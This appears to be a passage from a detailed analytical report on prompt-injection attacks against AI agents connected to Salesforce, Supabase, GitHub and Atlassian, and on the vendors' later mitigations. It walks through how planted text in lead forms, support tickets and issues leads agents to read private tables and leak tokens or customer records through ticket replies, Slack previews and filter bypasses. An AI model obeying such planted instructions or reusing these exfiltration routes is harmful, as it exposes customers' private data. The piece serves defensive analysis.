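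At the same time, Capsule disclosed a similar flaw in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's platform for building agents. The entry point was a form in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service. Capsule had reported the flaw in November 2025, and Microsoft patched it on 15 January 2026. Microsoft also gave it a CVE, recorded in MITRE's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026). Claw Times wrote that the patch did not fully prevent data from leaving. OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026), an AI-generated entry in a database of AI incidents, states that attackers had exploited both flaws in practice, but this seems to refer to Capsule's own tests.

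### SalesBleed: the same form a year later

Zenity disclosed SalesBleed, the most thorough of the 2026 cases, on 24 September, almost exactly a year after ForcedLeak. Like ForcedLeak, it began with a Web-to-Lead form and ended with an image, but by then Salesforce was enforcing Trusted URLs.

In Zenity's demonstration, an employee asked Agentforce to process a recent lead, and the agent treated text planted in the lead as part of its task. It looked up records in the tables for leads and for accounts, which hold a company's existing customers, and the researchers obtained company names, deal sizes and email addresses. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) quotes them as saying that the planted text "could have asked for anything" the agent's query tool could reach. Although they took only a few fields, the claim is reasonable because one general-purpose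 tool fetched them all.

The Trusted URLs filter misread certain domain endings and character sequences, so Zenity could write an address that got past it. Antipov reports that Agentforce sometimes showed the employee a message saying a security policy had blocked the content, even though the request carrying the data had already gone out. An employee who saw that message would have had no reason to report a leak.

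Attackers could also extract data through Slack, which automatically fetches any link in a message to show a preview. If Agentforce posted a link to an attacker's server with stolen data in the address, Slack sent the data there without anyone clicking. Zenity also found that an Agentforce action could reply in a company's Slack threads without asking anyone and without clearly showing who was behind the message. A stranger could therefore fill in a sales form and have the company's own agent post phishing messages to its employees.

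Salesforce received the report on 1 June 2026. It fixed the filter flaw on 18 August, and Zenity confirmed the last Slack fix on 21 September. Potentially dangerous actions in Slack now need a user's confirmation by default. 三村 (2026) writes in *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性*, a report for a Japanese security news site, that the flaws received no CVE and that there is no public evidence that anyone exploited them outside Zenity's tests.

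The three attacks that began at a lead form are fairly strong evidence that this kind of repair is incomplete. After Salesforce restricted web addresses, Capsule got data out by email. After Salesforce required approval for email, Zenity found a mistake in the address filter. Each fix was worth making and made the next attack harder to build. But an outsider could still write to the agent, the agent could still query customer records, and Salesforce had to find every route out before a researcher or a criminal did.

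### Who can write, and who has to act

A person had to start the agent in all the attacks described in detail so far. But in July 2025, *A Copilot Studio Story 2* (Sharbat, 2025) reported an attack on an agent that answers customers' emails by itself. Zenity had built a replica of a customer-service agent that McKinsey had made with Copilot Studio and Microsoft had used to promote the platform. When an outsider emailed the replica, it sent back records from its customer database. Microsoft fixed the flaw and paid Zenity $8,000. *Pwn the Enterprise* reports that Zenity found more than 3,500 Copilot Studio agents exposed to the internet, but not how many of them could reach private data.

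| Attack | Who can write | Check on the writer's identity | What an employee must do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copilot Studio replica, July 2025 | Anyone who can email the agent | None beyond an email address | Nothing |
| Atlassian helpdesk, June 2025 | Anyone who can use the support portal | Varies by company, from none to a customer account | Ask an agent to process the ticket |
| Jira and Cursor, August 2025 | Anyone who can email a support address that feeds Jira | None beyond an email address | Turn on auto-run and ask Cursor to handle the ticket |
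| Salesforce Einstein, August 2025 | Anyone who finds the support form | None | Ask about open cases |
| ForcedLeak, September 2025 | Anyone who finds the sales form | None | Ask about the lead |
| SalesBleed, September 2026 | Anyone who finds the sales form | None | Ask about the lead |

The last column matters less than it might seem, because an employee who asks about a new lead is doing their job, and training in spotting suspicious links would not stop them. Needing an employee does slow the attack and may give someone a chance to notice an odd answer. An agent that works through the queue by itself removes that chance, and the attacker can send it one version of the text after another and learn from the replies.

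Email raises the same problem for assistants that read an employee's inbox. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 3 December 2026) described three ways to steal data through Microsoft 365 Copilot that start with an incoming message.

### Why a helpdesk can't trust only known authors

GitHub's lockdown mode distinguishes insiders from outsiders, and an agent that sees only insiders' issues can still do much of its work.

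If a helpdesk applied the same restriction, its agent would have almost nothing to read, because most tickets come from customers rather than employees. The problem is even clearer with a sales form, which exists to collect messages from people the company has never heard of. Hiding those submissions from Agentforce would protect the database, but someone would have to read all the leads by hand.

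A company could instead require people to log in before they write. This would keep out anonymous attackers and give the company an account to block or investigate. The text still wouldn't be safe, because an attacker can sign up as a customer or, as in Cato's partner scenario, take over the account of someone the company trusts. Verifying an email address shows only that the writer controls it.

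Checks on the author also tend to fail when text moves between systems. If the Zendesk sync creates Jira tickets under its own account, a filter that checks the author will treat the stranger's text as coming from a trusted internal account and let it through. The filter would have to trace the text back to the original email, which works only if every system along the way records where the text came from.

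Limiting the agent makes more sense than limiting who can write tickets. Under the rule that David C endorsed for the National Cyber Security Centre, an agent that reads a customer's ticket should drop to that customer's privileges. It could look up the customer's own orders and search the public help pages, so a planted instruction could expose only what the customer could already see. However, the agent could no longer search other customers' tickets for the same fault, which is one of the more useful things a support agent can do. An employee would have to run that search separately and decide what to pass on. In a Supabase demonstration in July 2025, an agent without this limit read a planted support ticket and copied out a private table.

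## July 2025: a support ticket extracts a private Supabase table

Supabase hosts databases for app developers using Postgres, a widely used open-source database. Postgres has much finer access rules than GitHub's choice between public and private repositories, and can limit a customer to certain rows of a table. General Analysis, a start-up working on guardrails for tool servers, demonstrated that an agent could expose private data without breaking such rules. A customer's support ticket led the agent to copy a private table of access tokens into the ticket. Willison wrote about the demonstration on 6 July 2025, and a Hacker News discussion soon drew 478 comments, including some from Supabase and General Analysis.

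### Roles, row-level security and the service key

Every Postgres query runs under a role, which is much like a user account inside the database. An administrator decides, table by table, whether each role may read, add, change or delete rows. Postgres rejects any query that exceeds the role's privileges.

A support desk needs finer access control because all its customers' messages sit in one table. Row-level security (RLS) lets the administrator attach a condition, called a policy, that Postgres tests against each row. A policy might let customers see only the messages in their own tickets. If a customer requests every message in the table, Postgres returns only the rows that pass the test, without an error.

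Supabase depends heavily on these policies because many apps built on it let a visitor's browser query the database directly. The browser sends a public key, which anyone can find in the page, and the query runs under a role called `anon`. Once a developer turns on RLS, the public key gives no access to data until the developer writes a policy, according to Supabase's documentation as quoted in iknek's *The Double-Edged AI Sword*.

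Some jobs, such as sending invoices or deleting expired accounts, need access to every row. Supabase supplies a secret key for them. The key's role, `service_role`, is exempt from RLS, so Postgres doesn't test the policies when a query runs under it. *When AI Has Root*, Pomerium's detailed account of the demonstration, quotes Supabase's warning that such keys "should never be used in the browser or exposed to customers". Pomerium sells access controls for agents.

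The exemption is fairly safe in a billing script, because a developer wrote the queries in advance and a customer's message can't change them. An agent writes each new query after reading what the last one returned.

### General Analysis's support desk

General Analysis set up a Supabase project that imitated a company's support desk, with row-level security (RLS) on, and connected it to Cursor using the tool server's default settings. *Runtime Defense Against Prompt Injection in Supabase MCP*, a post by Tansive, which develops a tool for controlling agents, lists three tables: `support_tickets`, `support_messages` and `integration_tokens`. The last held API keys that nobody outside the company should see.

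Three parties used this database, each with a different role.

| Party | Role | Can read | Can write |
|---|---|---|---|
| Customer (the attacker) | `anon` | Their own ticket | Their own ticket and its messages |
| Support worker | A limited support role | Tickets and messages | Replies to tickets |
| Developer using Cursor | `service_role` | Every table | Every table |

The company in this scenario had been careful with the support worker, whose job is to read strangers' messages and who could not open the token table. But the developer's agent read the same messages with a key to everything. (Tansive's retelling has support staff using Cursor, but Willison and Pomerium both describe a developer.)

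### The attack on three rows

The following example is invented, but it uses the table names from the demonstration. Suppose that `support_messages` contains two rows:

| Ticket | From | Text |
|---|---|---|
| 41 | Ana | My invoice shows the wrong address |
| 42 | Attacker | Instructions for Cursor's agent, then a harmless question |

`integration_tokens` contains one:

| Customer | Service | Token |
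|---|---|---|
| Ana | Slack | EXAMPLE-7Q |

The attacker has already posted the message in ticket 42 through the public support form. The developer asks Cursor to show the latest open ticket. The agent looks up the database's structure, which gives it the names of the tables, and then fetches the messages in ticket 42. It follows the attacker's instructions and runs a query that selects every row of `integration_tokens`, which returns Ana's token. A second query inserts a new row into `support_messages`:

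| Ticket | From | Text |
|---|---|---|
| 42 | Support | Slack: EXAMPLE-7Q |

The attacker reloads the ticket page and reads the token. In Tansive's account, the attacker could then delete the message.

Postgres runs its checks at every step, and none of them fails:

| Step | Query | Role | Table privileges | Row-level security |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Attacker posts the message | Insert into `support_messages` | `anon` | Pass | Pass, because the row belongs to the attacker's ticket |
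| 2. Agent reads ticket 42 | Select from `support_messages` | `service_role` | Pass | Skipped |
| 3. Agent reads the tokens | Select from `integration_tokens` | `service_role` | Pass | Skipped |
| 4. Agent posts the tokens | Insert into `support_messages` | `service_role` | Pass | Skipped |
| 5. Attacker reloads the page | Select from `support_messages` | `anon` | Pass | Pass, because the new row belongs to ticket 42 |

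If the attacker had queried `integration_tokens` directly, Postgres would have returned nothing. In step 5, Postgres applies the policy correctly but still returns the token, because the agent has copied it into ticket 42, the attacker's own ticket. The policy checks which ticket a row belongs to, and Postgres does not record that the text in this row came from another table.

The developer had asked Cursor's agent only to show a ticket. In Invariant Labs' GitHub demonstration, the owner told the agent to "address" the issues, which was some reason to act on their contents. The developer's request gave no such reason, so the Cursor agent's mistake is harder to excuse.

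The planted message was also much cruder than the Pac-Man fan's suggestion. The attacker addressed part of it to Claude by name, told the company's support bot to ignore that part, and asked for the contents of the token table. The attacker also told the agent to hurry and write almost nothing in reply, which would have given the developer less to notice. A person who read the ticket would have seen at once that something was wrong. The same wording would probably fail more often against 2026 models, but Cursor's handling of the "apples" ticket a few weeks later suggests an attacker could have found subtler wording.

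The message named the `integration_tokens` table, but a real attacker might not know a company's table names. This is a fairly small obstacle, because the agent looks up the table names itself, so an attacker could describe the kind of data they want.

### What a narrower role would have changed

If the agent had connected with the support worker's role, Postgres would have rejected the query in step 3 whatever the ticket said, and the tokens would have been safe. But that role can read other customers' tickets, so a reworded message could still have made the agent copy Ana's complaint about her invoice into ticket 42.

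The agent could instead have dropped to the attacker's privileges after reading the attacker's text, as David C's rule requires. Postgres suits this because the database already has a role and policies for customers. Under those policies, the agent could not have read the tokens or Ana's message.

The rule gets stricter when an agent reads text from several people. The Hacker News commenter vidarh argued that such an agent should keep only the permissions that all the writers share. Ana and the attacker have access to none of the same private rows, so an agent that had read both their tickets couldn't look up private data for either of them.

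Tansive's developer built a less drastic defence, a filter that checks each SQL query against one of three profiles before it reaches Supabase. The support engineer profile allows access only to the two support tables, and the app developer profile allows access to everything except `integration_tokens`. The third profile, for the engineers who run the systems, lets the agent read the tokens but not the customers' messages, so that planted text never reaches an agent that can read the tokens. When the developer replayed the attack, the filter rejected the query for the tokens under the app developer profile and the query for the messages under the third profile.

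The app developer profile protects one table by name, so if the company later adds a table of payment details, the agent can read it until someone updates the rule. The third profile works only if whoever configures it knows every place where an outsider can write. The published configuration blocks reading only from `support_messages`. If customers can also write a subject line that the app stores in `support_tickets`, the agent can still read instructions that an attacker puts there.

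Support tickets are the most obvious place for an attacker to put instructions, but not the only one. Another Hacker News commenter, saurik, pointed out that the second line of a shipping address would also work. In an early copy of the thread on frontpage, Willison listed comments, feedback forms, error logs and the browser details that websites record for visitor statistics. An agent could read any of these while doing something unrelated to support. Most apps store text from strangers in many tables, so it is hard to keep a powerful agent away from all of it. It is usually easier to list the few tables the agent needs and give it a role that can access only those.

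Pomerium, which sells gateways, recommends using one here: a program between the agent and the database that could block access to the token table. It calls this "the only viable architectural choice", but that claim is too strong for this attack. A restricted Postgres role would block the same access without another product, as Tansive's developer acknowledges. He chose a filter because it also works with services such as GitHub and Stripe, which don't have Postgres roles.

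### Supabase's reply

A Supabase engineer replied in the Hacker News thread in July, and the company published a longer response, *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), on 16 September. Supabase accepted that the attack was possible but disputed how others had described it.

The company denied that MCP could "bypass" RLS, which it said remained "fully enforced", but added that a server may operate at a higher privilege, "as was this case". Both statements are accurate in the example above. Postgres enforced the policies on the attacker in steps 1 and 5, but skipped them for the agent in steps 2 to 4, when the theft took place. A customer who reads that RLS is fully enforced would reasonably assume that it limits the agent, which it didn't in this demonstration. Pomerium calls RLS "irrelevant" here, which is closer to the truth about the agent, though the policies did stop the attacker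 from taking the tokens directly.

Supabase also wrote that it had never offered a hosted tool server. Its server was open-source software that developers ran themselves or used through another company's product. In Tansive's configuration, for example, the developer's computer downloads Supabase's package and starts it with the developer's access token. Supabase's statement corrects a detail about where the program ran, but Supabase still wrote the program, and the agent's queries would have had the same effect from any machine. Supabase now runs a hosted server.

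The company said there had been no reported incident of a customer losing data through MCP. The demonstration doesn't contradict this, because General Analysis attacked its own test project. Willison was surprised by the lack of real attacks and suggested that too few people were using such servers to attract criminals. However, a theft of this kind would be easy to miss, because the queries come from a legitimate login and the stolen data appears briefly as a message in a support ticket. Another commenter suspected that the people most willing to give an agent full access are also the least likely to keep logs that would reveal a theft. The absence of reports is therefore some evidence that attacks were rare in 2025, but fairly weak evidence that there were none.

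The engineer complained that General Analysis had not followed Supabase's process for reporting vulnerabilities or answered its messages. A co-founder of General Analysis replied to him but did not address the complaint. Other commenters took the researchers' side. One objected that the only route Supabase listed was HackerOne, a platform for reporting vulnerabilities whose terms he considered onerous. Another asked what a private report would have achieved when the remedy was to add warnings for the model and the reader. Advance notice would still have let Supabase warn its customers before the method became public.

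The engineer's comment is good evidence that the attack worked. He said that Supabase had added mitigations a few weeks earlier, including text around query results that discourages the model from obeying instructions in them, and that the published attacks then "stopped working". In September, Supabase conceded that its guardrails had reduced the risk but not eliminated it.

General Analysis was also more modest in the thread than in its headline, "Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database". Its co-founder wrote that Supabase's server was technically not responsible for the problem. He blamed a combination of unsanitised data in the agent's context, models that can't tell instructions from data, and a Cursor agent with too much access.

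Supabase can't do much about how models read text, but it has considerable control over the agent's access because it chooses its server's default role. One commenter compared the server to an ordinary database, which isn't to blame when a badly written app sends it a harmful query. He added that Supabase could still narrow what its server accepts. This seems right, and it makes the co-founder's concession a little too generous.

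The headline goes beyond the demonstration, which leaked one table, but it fairly describes the agent's access, since `service_role` can read every table in the project.

### Keeping agents away from live data

Supabase's main advice in September was never to connect an agent to production data, meaning the database that real customers use. It said it had built the server for developing and testing apps, and recommended using test databases or anonymised copies instead.

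A test database with made-up rows would defeat the attack, because the attacker can't post a message in it and it contains no real tokens. A staging database, which developers use to try out changes, protects less if it is an unaltered copy of the live one, because it then contains the planted message and Ana's real token. The agent might still follow the planted instructions and write the token into ticket 42, but only in the copy, where the attacker can't see it. Using a copy would not prevent the agent from sending the token out in some other way.

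Developers can follow this advice only if they have a second database. Supabase acknowledged that many "vibe coders", people who build software mostly by instructing an AI, work directly on production and have no security team to stop them. According to the September post, the company first argued about the researchers' setup, then accepted that people do work this way. Its July documentation did not warn against using the server with a production database. Willison wrote in the thread that he wished it did, because he expected many people needed to hear it.

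### What read-only mode stops

When General Analysis published its demonstration, Supabase's documentation already recommended a read-only mode, as Willison noted in fairness to the company. He also quoted the documentation's stated reason, which was to keep the agent from making unintended changes. The documentation didn't connect the mode with theft, so a developer who trusted the agent not to break anything would have had little reason to switch it on.

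A developer turns on read-only mode by adding a setting to the server's address. Supabase then runs the agent's SQL as a Postgres user that cannot write. It also disables eleven other tools, including those for changing table structure and deploying code.

With this setting, step 4 of the example fails. The agent reads the ticket, follows its instructions and fetches the tokens, but Postgres rejects the insert, so the tokens don't appear when the attacker reloads the page.

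Postgres itself rejects the write, so the agent can't get around the restriction by rewording the query. Other servers have enforced read-only access less reliably. Datadog Security Labs reported in August 2025 that Anthropic's reference Postgres server, which was supposed to be read-only, could execute arbitrary SQL statements.

Steps 2 and 3 still succeed, so Ana's token ends up in the agent's context. The agent may show it to the developer, which is harmless if it goes no further. But if the developer has also connected a server that can send email or make web requests, the planted text can direct the agent to send the token out that way. Willison warned about such combinations in the thread. Cursor may not need a second server. A month later, *When a Jira Ticket Can Steal Your Secrets* (Willison, 2025) discussed an attack in which a Jira ticket directed Cursor to put a secret in a web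 address and visit it. In September, Supabase wrote that prompt injection was still the "number one concern" in read-only mode.

Approval prompts could catch the theft earlier. Supabase said that Cursor and Claude Code normally ask for approval before each tool call, and it recommended leaving this on. A developer who had asked to see a ticket would have good reason to reject a query on `integration_tokens`, which is easier to recognise as suspicious than a few stray lines in a reply. Supabase also warned that users may approve calls out of fatigue, and that attackers can push the important part of a query off the screen.

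Read-only mode is inconvenient for the people Supabase had in mind, who are building apps and want the agent to create tables and deploy code. The mode disables the tools for both. Developers can turn it on to investigate a ticket and off again to build, but they have to remember to do so each time. It is a better fit for someone who only asks questions about existing data.

### Similar claims about Neon and Heroku

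In the same thread, someone from Tramlines, which had also reported an attack on an AI email client, wrote that the company had found a similar exploit in the official server of Neon, another Postgres host. Willison called it "the exact same vulnerability", because a user can give Neon's server both read and write access to a database. Another commenter linked to a Tramlines post about an exploit of the tool server for Heroku, a platform for running web apps. The frontpage copy of the thread doesn't describe the method or results of either exploit, so these comments are much weaker evidence than the Supabase demonstration.

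The Neon claim is plausible because the attack needs only a database that holds both strangers' text and private data, and an agent that can read and write all of it. Neon advises users to give each person a separate key with the minimum permissions, and to monitor their agents' queries. Restricted permissions could have stopped the theft in step 3. Monitoring would probably have revealed a query on a table of tokens, but only after the attacker had a chance to copy them.

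## July 2025 to mid-2026: what the vendors changed in their tool servers

An agent can leak data only when it has access to private data, reads untrusted text and can send data out. A vendor that reliably removes one of these conditions stops the theft, whatever the model does. Supabase, GitHub and Atlassian all added protections after the 2025 demonstrations. A few of these do remove one of the conditions, but customers usually have to turn them on. The protections that the vendors turned on for everyone mostly make an attack harder.

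### Supabase's warnings around query results

In early summer 2025, Supabase began wrapping query results in warnings. Every user gets these warnings, and they don't interfere with any legitimate task.

The warnings also leave the whole trifecta in place. The model receives the warning and the attacker's message as one piece of text and may follow either. On Hacker News, the commenter tptacek compared this to cleaning up a stranger's JavaScript and then running it with full trust, an approach that "has never, ever worked". Another commenter, scott_w, wondered how to explain to a security team that the best protection available was a polite request to the model.

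Supabase also wrote automated tests that run the attack from start to finish against less capable models, which it considered easier to fool. Its engineer reported that the warnings had "significantly lowered" the attack's chance of success even against Anthropic's small Claude Haiku 3.5, but he gave no rates. Such tests are good at catching later changes that weaken the server, but they are much weaker evidence about new attacks because they only try wordings Supabase already knows. A test that used only Zenity's first Jira ticket, which Cursor refused, would have missed the "apples" version.

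Supabase also experimented with classifiers, which are models that screen text for dangerous content. In its September 2025 post, it listed the warnings and the classifiers under the heading "Where We Got It Wrong" and concluded that "guardrails alone aren't enough". It kept the warnings, but its documentation now says they are "not foolproof" and that a person should review the output before continuing.

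Supabase describes the warnings only for SQL results. Its server also has a `get_logs` tool, on by default, which returns a project's logs. Logs often record text that visitors send to an app, so text from a stranger may reach the agent without any warning around it.

### What a Supabase user gets without choosing any settings

Supabase's stronger protections are three settings that a user adds to the server's address. All three are optional. Supabase's list of options, as it stood in July 2026, gives the following behaviour:

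| Setting | If the user leaves it out | If the user sets it | Effect on the support-ticket attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_only` | The agent can change data | SQL runs as a user that cannot write, and other tools that change data are off | The agent reads the tokens but cannot post them in the ticket |
| `project_ref` | The agent can open every project in the organisation | The agent can open one project | None, because the tickets and tokens are in the same project |
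| `features` | Seven of the eight tool groups are on | Only the named groups are on | None, unless the user leaves out the `database` group |

Read-only mode is the most important setting here. Willison said it removes one part of the trifecta, though he still saw enormous risk in giving an agent even read access to a database.

Project scoping limits how much private data an attacker can reach. Suppose a developer runs a hobby forum and a client's online shop in the same Supabase organisation. Without scoping, an instruction planted in a forum post could make the developer's agent look up the shop's customers and write their details into the forum. Restricting the agent to the forum's project protects the shop's data from this attack, but an attacker could still reach the forum's private messages.

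The feature groups give users only coarse control. One tool in the `database` group, `execute_sql`, can read a stranger's ticket, read the private table and write the reply. To keep the useful part of that group without the dangerous part, a user has to turn on read-only mode as well. Supabase leaves the eighth group, storage, off by default to keep the number of tools down, which has little to do with security.

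Whether a new user gets the safer settings depends partly on where they copy the address from. The dashboard and the documentation generate an address with settings filled in. The setup example in Supabase's GitHub repository has the bare address, which lets an agent write to every project in the organisation. Supabase describes read-only mode and project scoping as "recommended by default", which a hurried reader could easily take to mean they are on.

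The restriction also disappears if someone deletes the setting, because the underlying login still permits everything. In July 2025, Supabase's engineer had promised finer permissions attached to the access token itself. But in May 2026, customers who registered their own application for the server still had to grant it write access to every available scope. Supabase also announced a "production mode" in September 2025 that would lock down riskier behaviour around real customer data, but the server's published options don't include it.

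The documentation has improved a good deal. It now explains a support-ticket attack almost identical to the one General Analysis demonstrated, and it includes the warning about production databases that Willison had found missing. This helps people who read the security advice before connecting an agent.

### GitHub's check for secrets

GitHub addressed the outbound channel first. In August 2025, it began checking tool calls involving public repositories for secrets. The check is free and on by default, and the hosted server blocks any call that fails it. GitHub has since extended the check to private repositories covered by its Advanced Security product.

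If the private README in Invariant's demonstration had also contained a cloud service key, the server would have blocked the agent's attempt to copy the text into the public `pacman` repository and returned the reason. GitHub advises users in this position to remove the secret and try again. An agent following a planted instruction could do the same, and its second attempt would publish the owner's salary and travel plans.

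The check can detect access tokens because they usually have a recognisable format. Salaries and travel plans don't, and GitHub acknowledged at launch that the check would not stop leaks of data other than secrets. An attacker might also get a real key past it by having the agent encode the key first, as the GitLab Duo attack did with source code.

Users who think the scanner is wrong can usually override it through a link in the error message. An override is necessary because scanners sometimes mistake harmless strings for keys. However, users who have opted out of the same protection for their own account can't override it. For everyone else, the override adds another prompt that a tired user may click through.

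In May 2026, GitHub (2026) released a second feature with a confusingly similar name. It lets developers ask an agent to scan their changes for exposed secrets before committing them. This catches a developer's own mistakes but does nothing against a planted instruction, because the scan runs only when someone asks for it. It also requires a repository with GitHub's Secret Protection product enabled.

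### The hidden-text filter and the Pac-Man issue

In December 2025, GitHub began filtering untrusted text in issues and pull requests before its server passes them to the model. The filter, which is on by default, removes invisible Unicode characters, unsafe HTML, and code-block text that GitHub doesn't display. In GitHub's example, a code block displays one harmless line of code but also contains a hidden instruction to list the user's private repositories. The filter deletes the instruction and keeps the code.

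A maintainer who reads an issue before handing it to an agent can now be fairly confident that the agent will receive the same text. Attackers have to write their instructions where people can see them, instead of hiding them as Legit Security did with white text in the GitLab Duo attack.

The filter would have had nothing to remove from the Pac-Man issue that Invariant Labs planted, because the issue was written in visible, plain English. The owner could have read it at any time but had asked Claude to do so instead. Attackers only need to hide instructions if a person is going to read the issue, and people connect agents to their issues partly to avoid reading them.

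### Lockdown mode

Lockdown mode, an opt-in setting that GitHub released at the same time, filters text in public repositories by author. When an agent tries to read an issue or pull request, the server checks whether the author has push access to the repository and returns an error if not. It also omits comments, reviews and sub-issues by authors without push access. This removes the untrusted-text part of the trifecta for the items it covers, and attackers can't get around the check by rewording an issue.

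Lockdown mode covers less than its description suggests. GitHub's June 2026 list of affected tools contains only `issue_read` and `pull_request_read`. In Ntousakis's reconstruction, Claude got the Pac-Man issue's planted text from `list_issues`, which isn't on the list. Lockdown mode would have withheld the issue if Claude had opened it with `issue_read`. GitHub's documentation for its automated workflows describes a broader filter that also covers discussions. A user who depends on lockdown mode should test whether it also hides a stranger's issue from `list_issues`.

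An attacker could also put instructions in a repository's files. In the server's code comments, GitHub classes the contents of public repositories as untrusted because outsiders can contribute to them through pull requests. But `get_file_contents`, the tool that reads files, isn't on the lockdown list. To plant the instructions, the attacker would first have to persuade a maintainer to accept a change containing them, which is considerably harder than filing an issue.

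Lockdown mode also does not apply to private repositories, on the assumption that only insiders write there. That is usually true of code, but it may not be true of issues if a company copies customers' emails into a private repository's tracker, as the company in Zenity's Cursor scenario did with Jira.

DevClass objected that the filter originally proposed would hide many useful contributions, and that objection also applies to lockdown mode. Under a fully effective lockdown mode, the owner of `pacman` might have had no issues left for Claude to address. GitHub says a workflow's owner may want to turn lockdown off for some jobs, including sorting new issues and detecting spam, provided that other safeguards are in place.

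### Faults in lockdown mode itself

The security company Aikido reported that the original permission check could return an incorrect result for whether an author had push access or whether a repository was private. Either error could lead the server to show an agent a stranger's text while the user believed lockdown mode was hiding it. The check also didn't handle trusted bots properly. Version 1.0.3 corrected the check. Aikido rated the flaw as high risk, but its notice includes no demonstration, so it's hard to tell how often the check failed in practice.

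Some users had the opposite problem and couldn't read anything. In March 2026, GitHub warned in its documentation that an automated workflow with lockdown mode on would fail at runtime unless the repository's owner had created a suitable access token for it.

*Reducing Prompt Injection Risk with GitHub MCP Lockdown Mode* (2026), from the Japanese IT company Classmethod, describes a similar failure in August, this time with a personal access token. The tester tried to read two issues in the repository where GitHub develops the tool server. Lockdown mode correctly withheld an issue by an outsider, but it also withheld one by an author who the tester assumed had push access.

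The error message showed that GitHub had denied the server's request for the author's permissions. The tester guessed that only a project's own collaborators can look these up, which fits a comment in GitHub's code that listing a repository's collaborators requires push access. It was correct to withhold an issue whose author the server couldn't check. But a developer who wants an agent to study another project's bug reports will get errors and probably turn lockdown mode off.

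The most serious documented fault affected companies that run one copy of the server for many people. GitHub promoted this arrangement in January 2026 as a way to spare employees from managing their own tokens. Each request carries the token of the person who made it, but according to the advisory in Docker's vulnerability database entry *CVE-2026-48529*, the server kept the connection of the first person to sign in and used it for everyone's lockdown checks.

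Suppose Dana signs in first and Omar second. When Omar's agent opens an issue, the server uses Dana's credentials to check the repository and the author's permissions. Dana may not have the same access to that repository as Omar, so the check can return the wrong result and the server can pass a stranger's text to Omar's agent. If Dana's token expires, every later check fails with an error for all users until someone restarts the server.

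GitLab's *CVE-2026-48529* (2026) rates the severity 6.0 out of 10 (medium) and lists every version from 0.22.0 up to the fix in 1.1.2 as affected. The rating seems about right. The advisory's test program proves that two users end up sharing one stored connection, but it doesn't deliver planted text to anyone's agent. To steal data, an attacker would still need an agent that obeyed the text and could send data out. Someone who is the server's only user isn't affected, because no one else shares the connection.

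This fault was an ordinary programming error, and it received a CVE, unlike the Pac-Man attack that lockdown mode was meant to address.

### Hidden tools, read-only mode and labels

In January 2026, GitHub's server began hiding tools that a user's token has no permission to use. If a token can't read security alerts, for example, the alert tools no longer appear in the list the model receives. GitHub presented this as a way to reduce clutter and failed calls. The change adds almost no protection, since GitHub would have refused those calls anyway.

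The hiding also works only with the older "classic" tokens. An agent with a fine-grained token sees every tool, and GitHub enforces the token's limits when the agent makes a call. People who sign in to the hosted server are asked to grant more permission when a tool needs it, and can refuse. None of this would have interfered with the theft from `pacman`. A single classic permission, `repo`, covers both reading private files and writing to public repositories, so any classic token that allows the attack also leaves the necessary tools visible.

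GitHub's read-only mode does remove part of the trifecta. It takes away every tool that changes data, even one the user has requested by name. In this mode, Claude could still have read the private README, but it couldn't have opened the pull request. It also couldn't have fixed anything in the game, which was the job the owner had given it. As with Supabase, the mode is optional, and it doesn't affect other tools the agent may have for sending data out.

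By mid-2026, GitHub had added a more promising scheme to the server's code, which labels each tool result as trusted or untrusted and as private or public. A list of issues is always labelled untrusted, even in a private repository, so the scheme is more cautious than lockdown mode. If a search returns results from several repositories and one is private, the whole result is labelled private, because GitHub reasons that an agent can copy any part of a result once it has read it.

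In the Pac-Man attack, the issue list would be labeled public and untrusted, and the README with the salary would be labeled private and trusted. A program that tracked these labels could then refuse to let the agent write to a public repository. The labels also show whether `get_file_contents` returned a public or private file, which Ntousakis had suggested the tool should report.

However, the labels don't block anything by themselves. GitHub leaves enforcement to a separate service, so the labels don't protect a user whose agent ignores them. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group GitHub Next, reports a similar limit in the company's automated workflows, where labels on private data could not yet prevent leaks between repositories.

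### Atlassian's controls for administrators

Atlassian first responded with a note advising customers on precautions. It called the use of agents with its products "a customer-elected action" and recommended giving agents minimal access, requiring human approval, vetting every source of tools, and logging everything an agent does. Logs may help a company discover a leak and work out what it lost, but only after the attacker has the data.

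Atlassian later gave administrators separate switches for reading, writing and searching through its tool server. They can set each switch differently for Jira and for Confluence, its product for internal documents. A change takes effect immediately for the whole organisation, so it doesn't depend on employees remembering to change their own configurations.

Switching off writing for the helpdesk would have stopped Cato's attack at the last step, but it would also have prevented the agent from answering customers. Because the switch covers a whole app, it can't single out the replies an attacker could see, which Willison wanted a person to approve. When administrators allow a type of access, tools that Atlassian adds later normally receive it without further review.

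Other controls limit which AI tools may connect. Atlassian lets administrators approve domains, restrict connections to known network addresses and turn off API tokens. By default, it accepts a list of AI companies it works with, including Anthropic and OpenAI, and administrators can block that list only as a whole. These rules keep out unapproved software, but they would not have hindered Cato's attacker, who relied on a support engineer's authorised copy of Claude.

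Another policy can stop employees' agents from reading other companies' Atlassian sites. It could keep out instructions planted on a business partner's site, but it doesn't apply to tickets that customers submit to the company's own helpdesk.

Hiding chosen content from agents is probably the most useful control against this kind of attack. Atlassian lets an administrator block an agent's access to a whole site, particular content, or everything with a given classification, such as confidential. Blocked Jira items don't appear in the agent's searches, and if it requests one directly, it gets the same response as for an item that doesn't exist. Employees' access doesn't change.

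A company could use this to remove either of two parts of the trifecta. It could hide customers' tickets from developers' agents, so those agents never read a stranger's text, or hide confidential projects from a support engineer's agent, so there are fewer secrets it could leak. The second option suits a helpdesk better because its agent has to read tickets, but it wouldn't protect one customer's ticket from an instruction in another's.

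This control requires Atlassian Guard Standard, a paid plan, and blocking by classification requires the more expensive Premium version. It has no effect on agents that connect with an API token, so hiding confidential projects protects them only from other agents. An administrator can close this gap by turning API tokens off, but any automated systems that depend on them will stop working.

### The changes side by side

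In the table, "narrows" means a change reduces a part of the trifecta without eliminating it, and "removes" means it eliminates that part, but only within the vendor's own tool server.

| Change | Effect on the trifecta | On by default? | What still gets through |
|---|---|---|---|
| Supabase: warnings around SQL results | None; discourages the model from obeying | Yes | Wordings that persuade the model anyway; text from logs |
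| Supabase: read-only mode | Removes the outbound channel | No, though the dashboard may fill it in | Private data into the agent's context, and out through other tools |
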